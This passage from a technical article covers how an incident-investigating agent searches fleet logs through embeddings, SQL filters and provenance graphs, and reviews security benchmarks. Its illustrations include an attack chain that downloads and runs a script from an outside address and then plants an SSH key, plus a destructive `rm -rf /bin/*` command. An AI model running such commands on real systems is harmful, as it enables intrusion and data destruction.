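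The comparison shows that reading only the beginning of a log is a poor strategy, but not how summaries compare with searching raw events or having a model read the whole log in batches. The team estimated that reading in batches would take 192 model calls instead of eight, but didn't test it. The evidence for combining several kinds of record is stronger. Network alerts alone gave a recall of 40 per cent because they contain no usernames.

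Cadet and colleagues sort the system's errors into three categories, which would also help an engineer debug a similar memory:

| What went wrong | Example | Fix |
|---|---|---|
| The queries didn't extract the fact | A list of the ten most frequent addresses omitted the attacker's eleventh server | Return a longer list |
| The summary didn't reach the prompt, or the answer was cut off | Claude found half the answers in one case with k = 3 | k = 7 raised recall to 100% |
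| The model misread the evidence | GPT-4 gave a machine's account name instead of the user's | Exclude machine accounts in the question |

Another case rose from 27 to 98 per cent when the team tripled the amount of text allowed in the prompt. The final results for Claude include both improvements, so the team chose some settings using the same cases it scored. This is normal during development, but it makes 94 per cent an optimistic estimate for new cases, even those with familiar attacks.

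### What counts leave out

A summary that lists only the most frequent events can omit a rare one. If a server ran 400 commands in an hour and the summary lists the top ten, a lone command that deleted a firewall rule won't appear. To prevent this, the program can copy into the summary any line whose template or command has been rare in the past month.

Counts also discard the order of events. Suppose someone adds a firewall rule blocking an address on web-31 and then deletes it, while on another host someone deletes the same rule and then adds it back. Both summaries report one addition and one deletion, but the address remains blocked only on the second host. The embeddings in *NLLog* also lose the order, because Ndichu and colleagues average the vectors of all events in a session. Recording the first and last times of each kind of event helps in simple cases, but when events alternate,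 the agent has to read the original lines.

How records are grouped can also hide a pattern. If an attacker tries one password on each of the 40 servers, each server's hourly summary shows a single failed login. Only a count by source address would show 40 attempts from the same place. Hourly summaries would also split an attack that runs from 03:58 to 04:03. Longer windows reduce this problem but make the results harder to read. In the Active Directory exercise, replacing three five-minute windows with one 15-minute window reduced Claude's recall from 96 to 62 per cent. The data no longer fitted into the prompt, and the model began to summarise steps instead of listing them.

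No set of counts can cover every question. If the program didn't count downloads by file type, a search for downloaded scripts depends on whether another summary mentions them. The program can add a new count later and apply it to old records if it has kept them. An agent can also write its own database queries during an investigation, as *SherAgent* (2026) does.

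## Training an embedding model on commands and logs

Engineers can train the embedding model on the records instead of rewriting the records as sentences. Training can teach a model that `wget` and `curl` both download files, though the program still has to filter by host and time. In the main experiment on command lines, training raised one model's score from 78 to 88 out of 100. Among the largest models tested, however, the trained model beat the best general model by only one point.

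### Pairs and the InfoNCE loss

According to *Granite Embedding R2 Models* (2025), developers typically train embedding models with a contrastive objective, which moves a query's embedding closer to relevant texts and further from irrelevant ones. The training data consists of pairs of texts whose embeddings should be close together. In each batch, a text's partner is its positive example and the partners of the other texts are its negatives, so nobody has to collect unrelated pairs.

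The usual measure of error is the InfoNCE loss, which *CLARC* (2026) applies to code search. For the i-th pair in a batch of k pairs:

```
Lᵢ = −ln ( exp(sim(xᵢ, xᵢ⁺) / τ)  /  sum over j = 1…k of exp(sim(xᵢ, xⱼ⁺) / τ) )
```

Here xᵢ is a text, xᵢ⁺ is its partner, and sim is the cosine similarity of their embeddings. The temperature τ is a positive number that the engineer chooses. The fraction is the partner's share of the total over all candidates, and the loss falls toward zero as that share approaches 1.

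Suppose a batch has three pairs. The command `curl -O http://example.com/a.sh` has a similarity of 0.8 to its partner, a `wget` command for the same file. It has a similarity of 0.7 to an `rsync` command that copies a folder, and 0.3 to a restart. With τ = 0.05:

```
similarities divided by τ:   16, 14 and 6
partner's share:             e¹⁶ / (e¹⁶ + e¹⁴ + e⁶) ≈ 0.88
loss:                        −ln 0.88 ≈ 0.13
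```

Training changes the model's parameters to reduce this loss. The `rsync` command accounts for nearly all of the remaining 0.12, so it receives nearly all of the push away from `curl`. With τ = 1, the shares would be 0.40, 0.36 and 0.24, and the restart would be pushed about two thirds as hard as `rsync`. A low temperature therefore concentrates training on the wrong answers that are hardest to tell from the right one.

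This causes trouble if a supposed negative is really a match. The fleet's log contains 3,600 restarts of the shop application among 1.8 million lines. If a batch contains one of them and 63 other random lines, there is a 12 per cent chance that the 63 include another restart, in which case training would push the two apart. The program should remove such duplicates before it forms batches.

The choice of pairs also determines what the model treats as similar. For a command log, each pair should contain two commands with the same purpose, rather than two from the same machine or hour, because the program can look up the machine and time in the commands' fields.

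### Making pairs when real logs are private

In *CmdCaliper*, Huang, Yang and colleagues (2024) describe two obstacles to collecting pairs from real logs. Labelling commands takes security expertise, and companies don't want to share commands that contain private information. They therefore had language models write the training data for their dataset, CyPHER.

The dataset began with 2,061 Windows commands from documentation and other public sources. A program repeatedly showed 12 of the commands collected so far to one of six language models and asked for four new ones. Once the collection reached 28,520 commands, GPT-4 Turbo wrote a partner for each, with the same purpose but preferably a different form. In one pair, both commands search the list of installed programs for Chrome, one with `reg query` and the other with PowerShell's `Get-ItemProperty`.

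Using several models made the commands more varied. In a trial with equal numbers of commands, six models together covered 70 per cent of 80 kinds of purpose, compared with 51 per cent for the best single model. Some of the pairs are flawed, including one that matches a Windows scheduled task with `cronjob schedule daily 00:00 /path/to/program`, which isn't a Windows command. Huang and colleagues accept small syntax errors as long as the purpose is clear.

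Pairs can also come from labels or from the order of events. *LogICL* (2025) treats log sequences with the same label as positives. *ContraLog* (2026), which needs no labels, hides some messages in a sequence, predicts their embeddings from the rest, and uses InfoNCE to match each prediction to the right message. Both systems detect abnormal logs, so their success wouldn't show that an engineer could find the right line by asking a question.

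The server fleet's own records can supply training pairs. Each decision record describes an action in prose and cites the log line of the command that carried it out. Three months of records provide up to 1,800 pairs of prose and command, although many describe the same few repairs. A language model running on the company's own hardware could write more questions about in-house scripts, which don't appear in public data.

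### What CmdCaliper gained

Huang and colleagues tested their models on 2,807 commands from Splunk's public collection of attack data. GPT-4 Turbo again wrote a partner for each command, and the embedding model had to find that partner among 1,000 wrong candidates.

The main measure is MRR@3, the mean reciprocal rank within the first three results. A query scores 1 if the right answer comes first, 1/2 if second, 1/3 if third and 0 otherwise. Four queries with the right answer at ranks 1, 1, 3 and 12 average (1 + 1 + 1/3 + 0) / 4 ≈ 0.58, or 58 on the paper's scale of 0 to 100.

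Edit distance, which counts the character changes needed to turn one command into another, scored 71.2. CmdCaliper comes in three sizes, each trained from the GTE model of the same size:

| Model | 30 million parameters | 110 million | 340 million |
|---|---|---|---|
| GTE before training | 82.4 | 78.2 | 84.3 |
| Best general model | 82.4 (GTE) | 83.2 (E5) | 88.1 (GTR) |
| CmdCaliper | 86.8 | 87.6 | 89.1 |

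The middle column shows the largest improvement, 9.4 points, but its starting model, GTE-Base, was unusually weak and scored lower than the smaller GTE model. The gain over E5-Base is 4.4 points. At the largest size, the gain over the best general model is 1.0 point. All these general models date from 2023 or earlier, so training might add even less to a good current model.

The small model's result is the most useful for an organisation that has to process its logs on its own hardware. With 30 million parameters, the model scored within 1.3 points of the best general model, which has more than ten times as many, and outperformed the other three large general models.

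Starting from a good embedding model raised the score considerably. The same 110-million-parameter network scored 70.4 when trained from random weights, slightly below edit distance. It scored 82.3 when trained from BERT and 87.6 from GTE-Base. Huang and colleagues suggest that pretraining helps because file names, folders and arguments contain ordinary words whose meaning carries over. The training was short, at roughly 860 steps (two passes through about 27,500 pairs in batches of 64).

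### An easier task than searching a real log

The test commands came from real attack data, but GPT-4 Turbo wrote the matching commands that counted as right answers. It also wrote the matching commands in the training data, so the trained model may have learned how GPT-4 Turbo rephrases commands, which may differ from how people and attackers vary them.

The wrong answers were also easy to reject. For each command, Huang and colleagues chose as wrong answers the 1,000 of the other 2,806 commands whose ChatGPT-written descriptions were least similar to its own. This kept genuine matches from counting as errors, but it also removed near-duplicates. A firewall rule with `-A` would probably never compete with the same rule with `-D`. In Kapoor and Khan's test on Python functions, such near-copies reduced the best model's success from 99 to 33 per cent, and the CmdCaliper test does not rule out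 a similar fall.

*Neurograf v1* (2026), which describes a family of Romanian language models, similarly warns that its synthetic pairs made the contrastive task "substantially easier than realistic large-scale retrieval". The paper therefore treats accuracy during training mainly as a sign that the training worked. The CyPHER results also don't show how well a trained model would match an engineer's question to a line from a Linux server, because the dataset consists of Windows and PowerShell commands and its queries are themselves commands.

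A second experiment used 1,523 attack commands from Atomic Red Team, a public collection sorted by technique, and needed no partners generated by a language model. Each model was given a fifth of a technique's commands as examples and had to score the rest above commands for other techniques. The base model's AUROC was 0.87, and GTE-Base's was 0.80. With four fifths as examples, the gap was smaller, at 0.94 and 0.90. This experiment is better evidence than the first that training helps a model recognise kinds of command, especially when it has few examples.

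### Training on logs alone

*SecEncoder*, from Microsoft, tested training a model from scratch, which takes far more compute. Removing duplicates cut the training data from a terabyte of security logs to 270 gigabytes, or 77 billion tokens. The largest version has 1.1 billion parameters and took about four weeks to train on 64 A100 processors, or some 43,000 processor-hours.

The developers trained the model to predict hidden tokens in log lines. They never hid quotation marks or other delimiters, because these are easy to predict and carry little information. They also built a tokenizer (the program that splits text into tokens) from the logs. It keeps terms such as `TTY` and `netns` whole, while BERT's tokenizer splits each in two.

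When searching for log lines with the same template, most versions of SecEncoder had a mean reciprocal rank of 0.76 on a scale of 0 to 1, slightly above the 0.75 for BERT and OpenAI's older embedding model. SecEncoder did much better in a test of similarity. Its largest version scored same-template pairs 0.46 higher on average than different-template pairs, compared with a difference of 0.10 for OpenAI's model. But in the search, that version scored 0.75, the same as BERT and OpenAI's model.

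The two results are compatible because a search depends only on the order of the scores. A model that always scores the right line 0.95 and the wrong ones 0.94 still ranks them perfectly. Comparing models by what their searches return is therefore more reliable than comparing the gaps between their average similarities.

SecEncoder did better at detecting abnormal logs, with an average F1 score of 0.88 against 0.78 for BERT when a classifier learned from labelled examples. But it was never trained to place related texts close together, and its vector for a line is the average of the line's token vectors. The experiment shows that training on many logs isn't enough to make a good search model, but it didn't test how well the same model would search after contrastive training.

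### Replacing names and numbers before embedding

Long paths and numbers can take up much of a command's text, so engineers may want to replace them with placeholders. *CogTax* (Alonso-Carracedo, Fernandez-Boullon and colleagues, 2026) tested this on 585 Linux commands. Experts had sorted the commands into four levels by how hard they are to understand and how much they change the system. A simple classifier then predicted each command's level from its embedding.

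The researchers prepared the text for four embedding models in four ways. They left it unchanged, replaced strings, paths and numbers with `<STR>`, `<PATH>` and `<NUM>`, put an instruction in front of it, or did both of the last two. These are the best results:

| Model | Best preparation | Correct levels |
|---|---|---|
| Multilingual E5-small | Placeholders | 88.5% |
| MPNet | Instruction | 87.5% |
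| LLM-Embedder | Placeholders | 85.3% |
| MiniLM | Placeholders | 84.8% |

Placeholders were best for three of the four models, but the paper gives only each model's best result, so it is unclear how much they improved on unchanged text. The task also favours placeholders, because the level of a command seldom depends on which file it uses. A classifier that used only the shape of each command's syntax was right 66 per cent of the time. It couldn't reliably separate commands that display information from commands such as `mkdir` that change something, because both can have the same shape.

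*Living-Off-The-Land Command Detection Using Active Learning* (Ongun, Stokes and colleagues, 2021) describes an earlier system, cmd2vec, which splits a command at spaces and punctuation and gives each piece a vector learned from the pieces that usually surround it. It replaces purely numerical pieces with a "number" token and pieces that occur only once, such as the made-up job name `getitman`, with a "rare" token. A classifier of malicious commands that used these vectors and some additional scores reached an F1 score of 96 per cent.

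Discarding rare pieces is the opposite of BM25's approach, which gives them the most weight. An investigator might be searching for the name `getitman`. Placeholders can also hide the consequences of a command. *Command-line Risk Classification using Transformer-based Neural Architectures* (Notaro, Haeri and colleagues, 2024) rates `rm -rf /bin/*` as high-risk because it deletes the system's programs. Replacing the path with a placeholder turns it into `rm -rf <PATH>`, and a command that empties a temporary folder becomes the same text.

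A program can avoid this loss by embedding a version of the text with placeholders and storing the original values in fields and in a word index. It should leave command names and flags unchanged, and developers should test whether to replace paths as well. If the program replaces only values such as hostnames, times and process numbers, the deletion of `/bin` remains recognisable.

### When training pays and how much data it needs

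Engineers should first try a good current embedding model with filters for host and time. If searches fail because the program searched the wrong host or the log line is missing, training won't help. Training is worth trying when the model often misses commands that the engineer described in other words, or when the organisation can run only a small model. CmdCaliper reports a larger gain over the best general model of the same size for its small model than for its large one.

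CyPHER's 28,520 pairs were enough for a measurable gain from a good starting point, but Huang and colleagues didn't test smaller sets, so the minimum is unknown. In a classification study, Notaro and colleagues trained a small BERT model on 71,164 public Bash scripts for ten days on one processor, then trained it further on commands with risk labels. The resulting model needed about a tenth as many labelled commands as other methods to reach a similar F1 score.

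For the fleet, a reasonable first attempt would train on the decision records and tens of thousands of synthetic pairs based on its own kinds of command. The test questions should come from people and not appear in the training data. Training on a narrow task can make ordinary search worse, as S and colleagues found with LIMIT. The engineers should therefore search the incident notes with the general model unless the trained one does at least as well on them.

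Adding a server shouldn't require retraining the model. If placeholders replace hostnames, a restart on web-41 has the same text as one on web-03, and the filter handles the new name. New applications and log formats are more likely to cause problems. One version of SecEncoder correctly predicted 90 per cent of hidden tokens in logs like its training data, but only 36 per cent in logs from a different distribution. This comparison doesn't measure how quickly a model's accuracy falls as logs change over time.

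The fleet's engineers could rerun the same set of questions every month and after every major software change, adding questions about new commands. They should retrain when the results get clearly worse or when a newer general model outperforms the trained one. Retraining on a schedule alone would replace every stored vector without evidence of a benefit.

### Replacing the stored vectors

Each trained model arranges its vectors differently, so query vectors from a new model don't match the old vectors in the store. Vejendla (2025), in *Drift-Adapter*, measured this on three sets of a million texts. Searching the old vectors with the new model's queries gave 59 to 72 per cent of the recall that the new model achieved with its own vectors.

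Vejendla proposes an adapter, a small function that maps the new model's query vectors into the old model's vector space. The adapter is fitted on a sample of 20,000 texts embedded with both models. In Vejendla's text experiments, adapters recovered 95 to 99 per cent of the new model's recall.

Zhao, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *When the Bill Falls*, argue that this comparison is misleading, because an adapter is worth using only if it does better than keeping the old model. In one of their cases, replacing MiniLM with a newer model raised recall@10 from 0.83 to 0.88. An adapter would need about 95 per cent of the newer model's recall to match MiniLM, but the best of five types reached 64 per cent. Across 15 pairs of models, adapters beat the old model in only one, by at most 0.004.

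Vejendla counts a result as correct if the new model would also return it, while Zhao and colleagues use passages already judged relevant to each query, which is closer to what an engineer needs. Both studies cover changes between separately released models. A further-trained copy of the same model might stay closer to the original, and an adapter might then work better. Training only the part of the model that embeds queries would keep the stored vectors valid, but Wikum and colleagues found it hard to learn good query vectors for fixed document vectors.

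A store too large to rebuild quickly can switch to the new model gradually. The old index finds 50 candidates for each query, and the program embeds them with the new model and reranks them. In the MiniLM case, this came within 0.003 of the new model's recall after embedding 26 per cent of a million passages. Embedding the candidates slowed a query by as much as 187 milliseconds, or by more when background work delayed it. The program still has to embed all the remaining items before it can retire the old index.

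The fleet's store is small enough to rebuild at once. Vejendla estimates about 100 processor-hours for a million items in one table and 0.5 to 1 in another. For 1.8 million log lines, that means between one and 180 processor-hours, probably near the low end because the lines are short. A second set of vectors, each with 768 four-byte numbers, takes 5.5 gigabytes. If the program embeds the commands with placeholders, identical texts can share a vector, so the 3,600 restarts need only one.

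The program builds the new index alongside the old one and adds new items to both. The engineers then run the same test questions on both indexes and switch only if the new one is clearly better. In Zhao and colleagues' data, 250 questions with known answers were enough to confirm an improvement of about two percentage points or more. The program must keep the original text of every item, because it can't compute new vectors from old ones. It should also record which model produced each vector, so that a search never mixes vectors from different models.

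## Searching by field, time and link

A database can find one restart among 3,600 without embeddings if the host and time have their own columns. The program stores each parsed record as a row in a table, and the agent writes a query specifying the values it wants. The result is exact, but the agent has to know which column to search and what to look for.

### The hour before an outage

Suppose the agent returns to the outage of 14 September and wants to know what anyone did on web-17 in the hour before the errors began at 02:10. In SQL, the standard language for querying tables, the question is:

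```
SELECT time, user, cmd, exit
FROM   commands
WHERE  host = 'web-17'
  AND  time >= '2026-09-14T01:10:00Z'
  AND  time <  '2026-09-14T02:10:00Z'
ORDER BY time;
```

The database returns every row that meets all three conditions. Shortened, the result might be:

```
01:34:12  deploy  df -h                                  0
01:47:30  deploy  sudo apt-get install shop-app=3.8      0
01:48:05  deploy  sudo systemctl restart shop-app        0
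…
(23 rows)
```

If the query returns 23 rows, the table holds exactly 23 commands from that hour. The query won't miss the upgrade just because the command is worded differently from the question. A similarity search returns a fixed number of lines, k. With k = 10 it would miss at least 13 of the commands, and with k = 100 it would add at least 77 lines from other machines or hours.

The result is complete only for what the table contains, so it misses commands that the machine didn't log and lines that the parser couldn't split. The tool that runs the query may also cut a long result to save tokens, so the agent should first run `SELECT COUNT(*)` with the same conditions to learn how many rows to expect.

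If the cause might lie on another server, the agent can remove the host filter. At 500 commands per server per day, the search then returns about 830 rows for the hour, or 42,000 tokens, which Claude Opus 5.5 could read for 17 cents. For longer periods, the agent can have the database count the commands by host and read only the unusual ones.

The agent also needs a way to find out which tables exist. In *CTI-REALM* (2026), a benchmark in which agents write rules for detecting attacks, one tool lists the tables, another returns a table's columns and a third runs a query. With these tools, an agent can answer questions that a fixed library of queries doesn't cover. The agent's database account should be read-only, so that a badly written query can't change the records.

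### Following links from an alert

Some questions concern a chain of events whose host and time the agent doesn't know in advance. For these, a program can turn the records into a graph. The nodes are processes, files, users and network connections, and each event links two of them. On web-22, after the password logins of 3 November, the host records might give these links:

```
time       subject          relation       object
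03:13:20   wget (5144)      connected to   198.51.100.24
03:13:21   wget (5144)      wrote          u.sh
03:13:31   bash (5149)      read           u.sh
03:13:32   bash (5149)      started        python3 (5153)
03:13:34   python3 (5153)   wrote          authorized_keys
```

The file `authorized_keys` lists the keys that allow someone to log in without a password. Suppose a monitor raises an alert because a program changed this file. The agent looks up which process wrote the file and finds `python3`. It then finds that `bash` started `python3` after reading `u.sh`, and that `wget` had written `u.sh` after connecting to 198.51.100.24. A search for that address in the login table returns the four failed logins and the successful one.

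The agent can then follow the links forwards. It can check what else `python3` wrote and whether any other server connected to the same address. None of this needs a special database, because the links fit in an ordinary table and each step is a query:

```
SELECT time, subject
FROM   links
WHERE  host = 'web-22' AND object = 'u.sh' AND relation = 'wrote'
  AND  time <= '2026-11-03T03:13:31Z';
```

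The last condition matters because only earlier events can be causes. Without it, the agent would also follow links from processes that wrote to the file after `bash` read it.

### What the graph costs

Every event adds a link, so the number of links grows in proportion to a machine's activity, which is far greater than its command log shows. *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations* (Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues, 2026) gives figures for short recordings. Five recordings of ordinary activity on lab machines, totalling 30 minutes, produced 7,136 links, or about four a second. One-minute recordings from five machines in OpTC, a large public collection, produced 34,048, or about 113 a second.

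At those rates, the 40 servers would produce between 14 million and 390 million links a day, compared with 20,000 commands. Over three months, they would produce at least 1.2 billion links. Engineers may therefore have to delete links after a few weeks or leave out routine ones, such as those created when programs read their own libraries.

The graph is still smaller than the logs it was built from, because the conversion removes repeated events. The 30 minutes of ordinary activity produced 30,232 raw log lines. On Windows, where the recorder writes much more, the conversion reduced one five-minute recording from 1.2 million lines to 5,198 links.

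The number of paths grows faster than the number of links. If every node links to ten earlier ones, going four steps back from an alert can reach 10,000 nodes. The agent therefore has to choose which links to follow at each step, for example by ignoring files that almost every process reads. Anand and colleagues also mention that recording the graph slows the machines down and that people need time to interpret it.

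Connecting the graph to other logs takes more work. For *SecLog-Bench*, Wang, Xu and colleagues (2026) joined host records to application logs and network traffic in 29 simulated attacks. Matching times wasn't enough, because one web request can set off many events on the host, and network equipment may change an address on the way. So they added code to the running applications to record which request led to which event. They needed separate versions for Python, Java, Node.js, and PHP and C, although scenarios that used the same language could share most of the code.

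The joined records can show things that no single log can. In one example, the application log shows a request that tries to make a web server print its list of accounts. The server reports success, but that doesn't prove that the command ran. A host record shows that it did, and the network traffic shows that the list left the server. Even with the links in place, language models interpreted such evidence poorly. When Wang and colleagues asked eight models how far an attack had progressed, the best was right 44 per cent of the time. Guessing would have been right 25 per cent of the time, because the four possible answers were equally common.

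### Investigating attacks on a fictional company

*ExCyTIn-Bench* (Wu, Velazco and colleagues, 2026; first released in 2025) tests how well agents investigate attacks by writing their own SQL queries. It uses logs from Alpine Ski House, a fictional company with a Microsoft cloud account. The team copied eight real attacks and collected 57 tables, each with 8 to 139 columns. Each attack has an average of 365,000 rows, and the full 44 days of logs have 14.3 million.

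The questions come from a graph of the alerts that Microsoft's security products raised during the attacks. Each alert lists the users, addresses, files and other things involved, and the team linked the alert to each of them. For each question, a program chose two alerts. A language model received the first as background and wrote a question whose answer was something linked to the second. For example, one question describes a login from an anonymous address and asks for the identifier of the account behind a suspicious mailbox rule. This method produced 7,542 questions, of which 589 form the test.

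The agent isn't told what the tables contain. At each turn it can run one query, which returns at most 15 rows, or submit an answer. It has 25 turns. A correct answer scores 1, and a wrong one can still score points if it includes findings from the path between the two alerts:

```
the finding one step before the answer     0.4
the finding two steps before               0.4² = 0.16
both                                       0.56
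```

These are some of the average scores:

| Model | Score |
|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 0.293 |
| o3 | 0.456 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 0.487 |
| GPT-5.1, high reasoning | 0.582 |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 0.606 |

Microsoft (2025) also reports 56.2 per cent for GPT-5 with high reasoning and a drop of nearly 19 per cent at lower settings. A language model graded the answers and accepted a list of several values if one of them was right. Its grades matched human judgement on all 163 answers that Wu and colleagues checked.

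An experiment with GPT-4o, limited to 15 turns, shows what made the questions hard:

| Tables in the database | Logs of one attack | Logs of all 44 days |
|---|---|---|
| Alerts and raw logs | 0.260 | 0.248 |
| Raw logs only | 0.213 | 0.184 |
| Alerts only | 0.459 | 0.382 |

When the database held both alert tables and raw logs, making it about 39 times larger hardly lowered the score. The questions tend to include a date, and filtering by date excludes most of the added rows. Similarity search has no such filter to exclude added records as a store grows. Removing the raw logs raised the score sharply, but mainly because the questions were built from the alerts. The benchmark therefore partly measures how quickly an agent finds the alert tables. The scores on raw logs are more relevant for servers without security products that raise alerts.

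The best models in that test are now a year old. Kassianik, Nelson and Singer (2026), in *Beyond Success Rate*, tested newer ones on BOTS v1, a public exercise from the log-search company Splunk. It has 31 questions about a defaced website and a ransomware infection, and the agents wrote queries in Splunk's own language. They received the answers to earlier questions where a later one depended on them, and hints after wrong answers. Because the solutions have been public for years, the researchers also ran the models without any tools:

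| Model | With searches | Without tools |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 93.9% | 74.8% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 92.1% | 39.3% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91.4% | 77.2% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 19.9% |

Opus 4.8 had the highest score, but it could earn most of its points without seeing a log. Fable 5's result is better evidence of skill at searching, since it gained almost 70 points from the tools with about three calls per question. DeepSeek v4 Flash made about 48 calls per question and scored 73.0 per cent, and doubling its budget added less than a point. Kassianik and colleagues suggest that agents often make extra searches after missing the important field. The percentages are approximate, because a later run of GPT-5.6 Terra produced a different score, 77.9 per cent.

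### Reading host records for signs of an attack

Anand and colleagues' benchmark, AuditBench, appeared in June 2026 and tests a different skill. The models don't search. A program splits a recording into pieces, and the model reads every piece. There are 51 recordings, 25 from the lab and 26 from OpTC, and 15 of them contain only harmless activity. The models have to do four jobs that follow an alert:

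- decide whether the alert is real
- find changes that would let an attacker keep access to the machine
- find connections that would let an attacker control another machine
- find data that left the machine

For each finding, the model gives details such as the time, the file or the other machine, and a program checks them against the known facts. The table shows the combined results for both sets of recordings when the models read links instead of raw lines, with false alarms in brackets.

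| Model | Real alerts | Kept access | Reached another machine | Data taken |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 10 of 10 (15) | 5 of 9 (3) | 2 of 24 (3) | 7 of 7 (3) |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 10 of 10 (134) | 8 of 9 (42) | 11 of 24 (45) | 7 of 7 (37) |
| GPT-5 mini | 7 of 10 (12) | 7 of 9 (8) | 5 of 24 (12) | 5 of 7 (4) |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 10 of 10 (133) | 7 of 9 (25) | 12 of 24 (41) | 7 of 7 (18) |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 10 of 10 (24) | 4 of 9 (18) | 5 of 24 (19) | 3 of 7 (5) |

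Gemini 2.5 Pro flagged all ten real alerts but also 134 of 166 harmless pieces, so its flags were of little use. GPT-5 gave few false alarms but missed 22 of the 24 connections to other machines. These models date from 2025, and current ones would probably do better. The tests also included few attacks.

File and task names misled the models most often. At least four of the five models shared 19 false alarms, and in 18 of these their explanations relied heavily on such a name. One was a scheduled task named `clear_logs`, which OpTC's creators had labelled harmless. An agent that can run queries should check what such a task did before reporting it. But the models usually made different mistakes. About 350 false alarms each came from only one or two models, so requiring three to agree would remove most false alarms but also lose some real findings.

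Links used fewer tokens than raw lines, but they didn't always lead to better answers. On recordings available in both forms, Llama 4 Maverick did better with links in all four jobs, while Gemini 2.5 Pro did at least as well with raw lines in all four. A more detailed prompt raised GPT-5 mini's F1 score for finding stolen data from 0.12 to 0.62, although the researchers wrote it after examining false alarms in some of the same recordings.

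Reading everything is too expensive for a fleet. A piece of 400 links takes about 100,000 tokens, so reading even 14 million links with Opus 5.5 each day would cost almost $14,000 a day. The agent therefore has to choose what to read, and it can choose wrongly.

### How queries fail

An agent that doesn't know the tables starts by guessing. In a run that Wu and colleagues describe, GPT-4o had to find a login from a certain address at 11:01:27 on 17 July. It first filtered on a column called `Timestamp`, which didn't exist, and the database returned an error. It then listed the columns, found `TimeGenerated` and searched for the exact second, but got no results. When it searched the whole day, it found the login. It took 16 actions to reach the answer, while the reference solution had two steps. Across models, the share of queries that succeeded had a correlation of 0.86 with the score.

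The error did no harm because the agent could see it. The empty result was more dangerous, since an agent that stopped there would have concluded that nobody had logged in. To tell absence from a bad query, the agent can remove one condition at a time. Suppose it is looking for firewall changes on web-31:

```
web-31, 01:00–04:00, command contains "iptables"      0 rows
web-31, 01:00–04:00                                   0 rows
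web-31, whole day                                   438 rows
```

About 60 commands would be normal for those three hours, so the log probably has a gap. If the second query had returned 60 rows, the first result would have been useful evidence, provided that no other command could have changed the firewall.

A filter on the wrong field can be hard to notice because it still returns plausible rows. Suppose an investigator asks for everything the deploy account started on web-03 on 21 October. A query for process records with `user = 'deploy'` misses the nginx reload, because deploy ran it through `sudo` and the record lists root as the user. The agent can catch this by checking whether the results include an event it already knows about, such as the reload in the command log.

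The agent may also choose the wrong table. In CTI-REALM, part of the score depends on finding the tables that hold the evidence. *Unconstrained CTI-REALM with Open-Weights* (2026) points out that an agent could get full marks for this part by inspecting all 12 tables, so the paper instead scores the tables used in the agent's final query. On the benchmark as a whole, Claude Opus 5 scored 0.69 and GLM-5.3-flash scored 0.74, so recent models still have room to improve.

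Queries help least when the agent can't say what it is looking for. *Cyber Defense Benchmark* (Chona, Kozlov and Kumar, 2026) gave agents a database of 75,000 to 135,000 Windows records and asked them to find the malicious events, with no specific questions or hints. The best of five models, Claude Opus 4.6, found an average of 3.8 per cent of them. An agent asked "which address did the malware contact?" knows what kind of record to look for, but these agents had no such clue. The test dates from April 2026, so the figure may be out of date, but the gap between this result and the scores on BOTS v1 is probably too large for newer models alone to explain. *DiagChain* (2026) reaches a similar conclusion from several recent benchmarks, where success depended on the scope of the search and the length of the path to the answer.

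An agent without a lead can start with standard counts that find, for example, commands that ran for the first time this month or addresses that contacted many servers. Each unusual result gives it a value to search for next.

### Filtering first, then ranking by similarity

Vector search works well for finding past incidents, which can also provide a lead. When web-19 returns 502 errors on 5 October, the agent needs the September note because it describes similar symptoms. An SQL condition can't test for similar symptoms unless someone has already sorted incidents into categories.

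Wu and colleagues tested Expel, a method that gives an agent a similar earlier investigation and rules drawn from practice questions. GPT-4o scored 0.390 with it, compared with 0.354 with three fixed examples and 0.260 with neither. It also needed 9 turns instead of 11, but each run cost about 1.6 times as much because the prompt was longer. The test doesn't show how much of the gain came from the earlier investigation and how much from the rules. The practice questions covered the same eight attacks as the test, so an investigation of a different incident would probably help less.

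A memory can combine both kinds of search in one query. The fields exclude items that can't apply, and similarity ranks the rest:

```
SELECT id, text
FROM   notes
WHERE  app = 'shop-app' AND version = '3.8'
ORDER BY cosine_distance(embedding, :alert_embedding)
LIMIT  5;
```

The order of filtering and ranking matters. Suppose a program fetches the 100 lines in the whole command log that are most similar to the query, then keeps those from web-17 in the hour before the outage. Only 23 of the log's 1.8 million lines are from that host and hour. If similarity is unrelated to host and time, the chance that at least one of the 23 is among the 100 is about one in 800. A program that filters first keeps all 23 and can return them without ranking. Ranking is useful when more items remain than the agent can read.

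A strict filter can also exclude the right item. A note about version 3.7 might explain the crash of version 3.8, but the query above would never return it. The program should filter only on conditions that must hold. If the question names a host or a period, the program can safely filter on it, as long as the fields are correct. When an item from another version might help, the agent can search with the version filter first and then without it. When ranking the results, the program can also use rank fusion to combine similarity with word matching.

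For the alert on web-19, the agent would start with the notes. The September note suggests that the application is running out of memory, so the agent queries the host records of web-19 for processes that exited for lack of memory since the errors began. If it finds several, it checks the installed version and the current limit on the machine, and then raises the limit. If it finds none and the records have no gap, the note probably doesn't apply, and the agent instead lists every command from the hour before the errors.

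## Testing the memory on the records it will serve

A memory that scores well on public benchmarks may still fail on the fleet's records, so the engineers need a test built from those records. A few hundred questions are enough to start. Most of the work is finding every record that answers each question.

### Building the test set

Test questions should come from real work, such as incident reports, tickets and queries the agent wrote during past repairs. Questions someone invents while reading the log tend to repeat its wording, which makes word matching look better than it is.

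Some of the test prompts should be tasks rather than questions. *DolphinBench* (2026) contrasts asking which messaging platform a team uses with telling the agent to post an update in the team's channel. The agent can tell from the question that it needs a stored fact, but not from the instruction. On the fleet, "What memory limit does version 3.8 need?" is a question, and "Fix the 502 errors on web-19" is the matching task. *Your Agents Are Aging Too* (Zhu, Ro and colleagues, 2026) tested the same stored facts in both forms and found lower accuracy with tasks. Most of the failed replies still looked complete.

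A set of 200 could look like this:

| Kind | Example | Number |
|---|---|---|
| One event | When did deploy restart shop-app on web-03 on 21 October? | 50 |
| Complete list | Which servers did the agent change after the 3.8 upgrade? | 40 |
| Similar incident | Have we seen 502 errors like these before? | 40 |
| Changed fact | Which server has the address 10.0.4.23 now, and which had it on 10 September? | 30 |
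| No answer | Who changed the firewall on web-31 last night? (Nobody did.) | 20 |
| False premise | Why did the agent lower the memory limit on web-17? | 20 |

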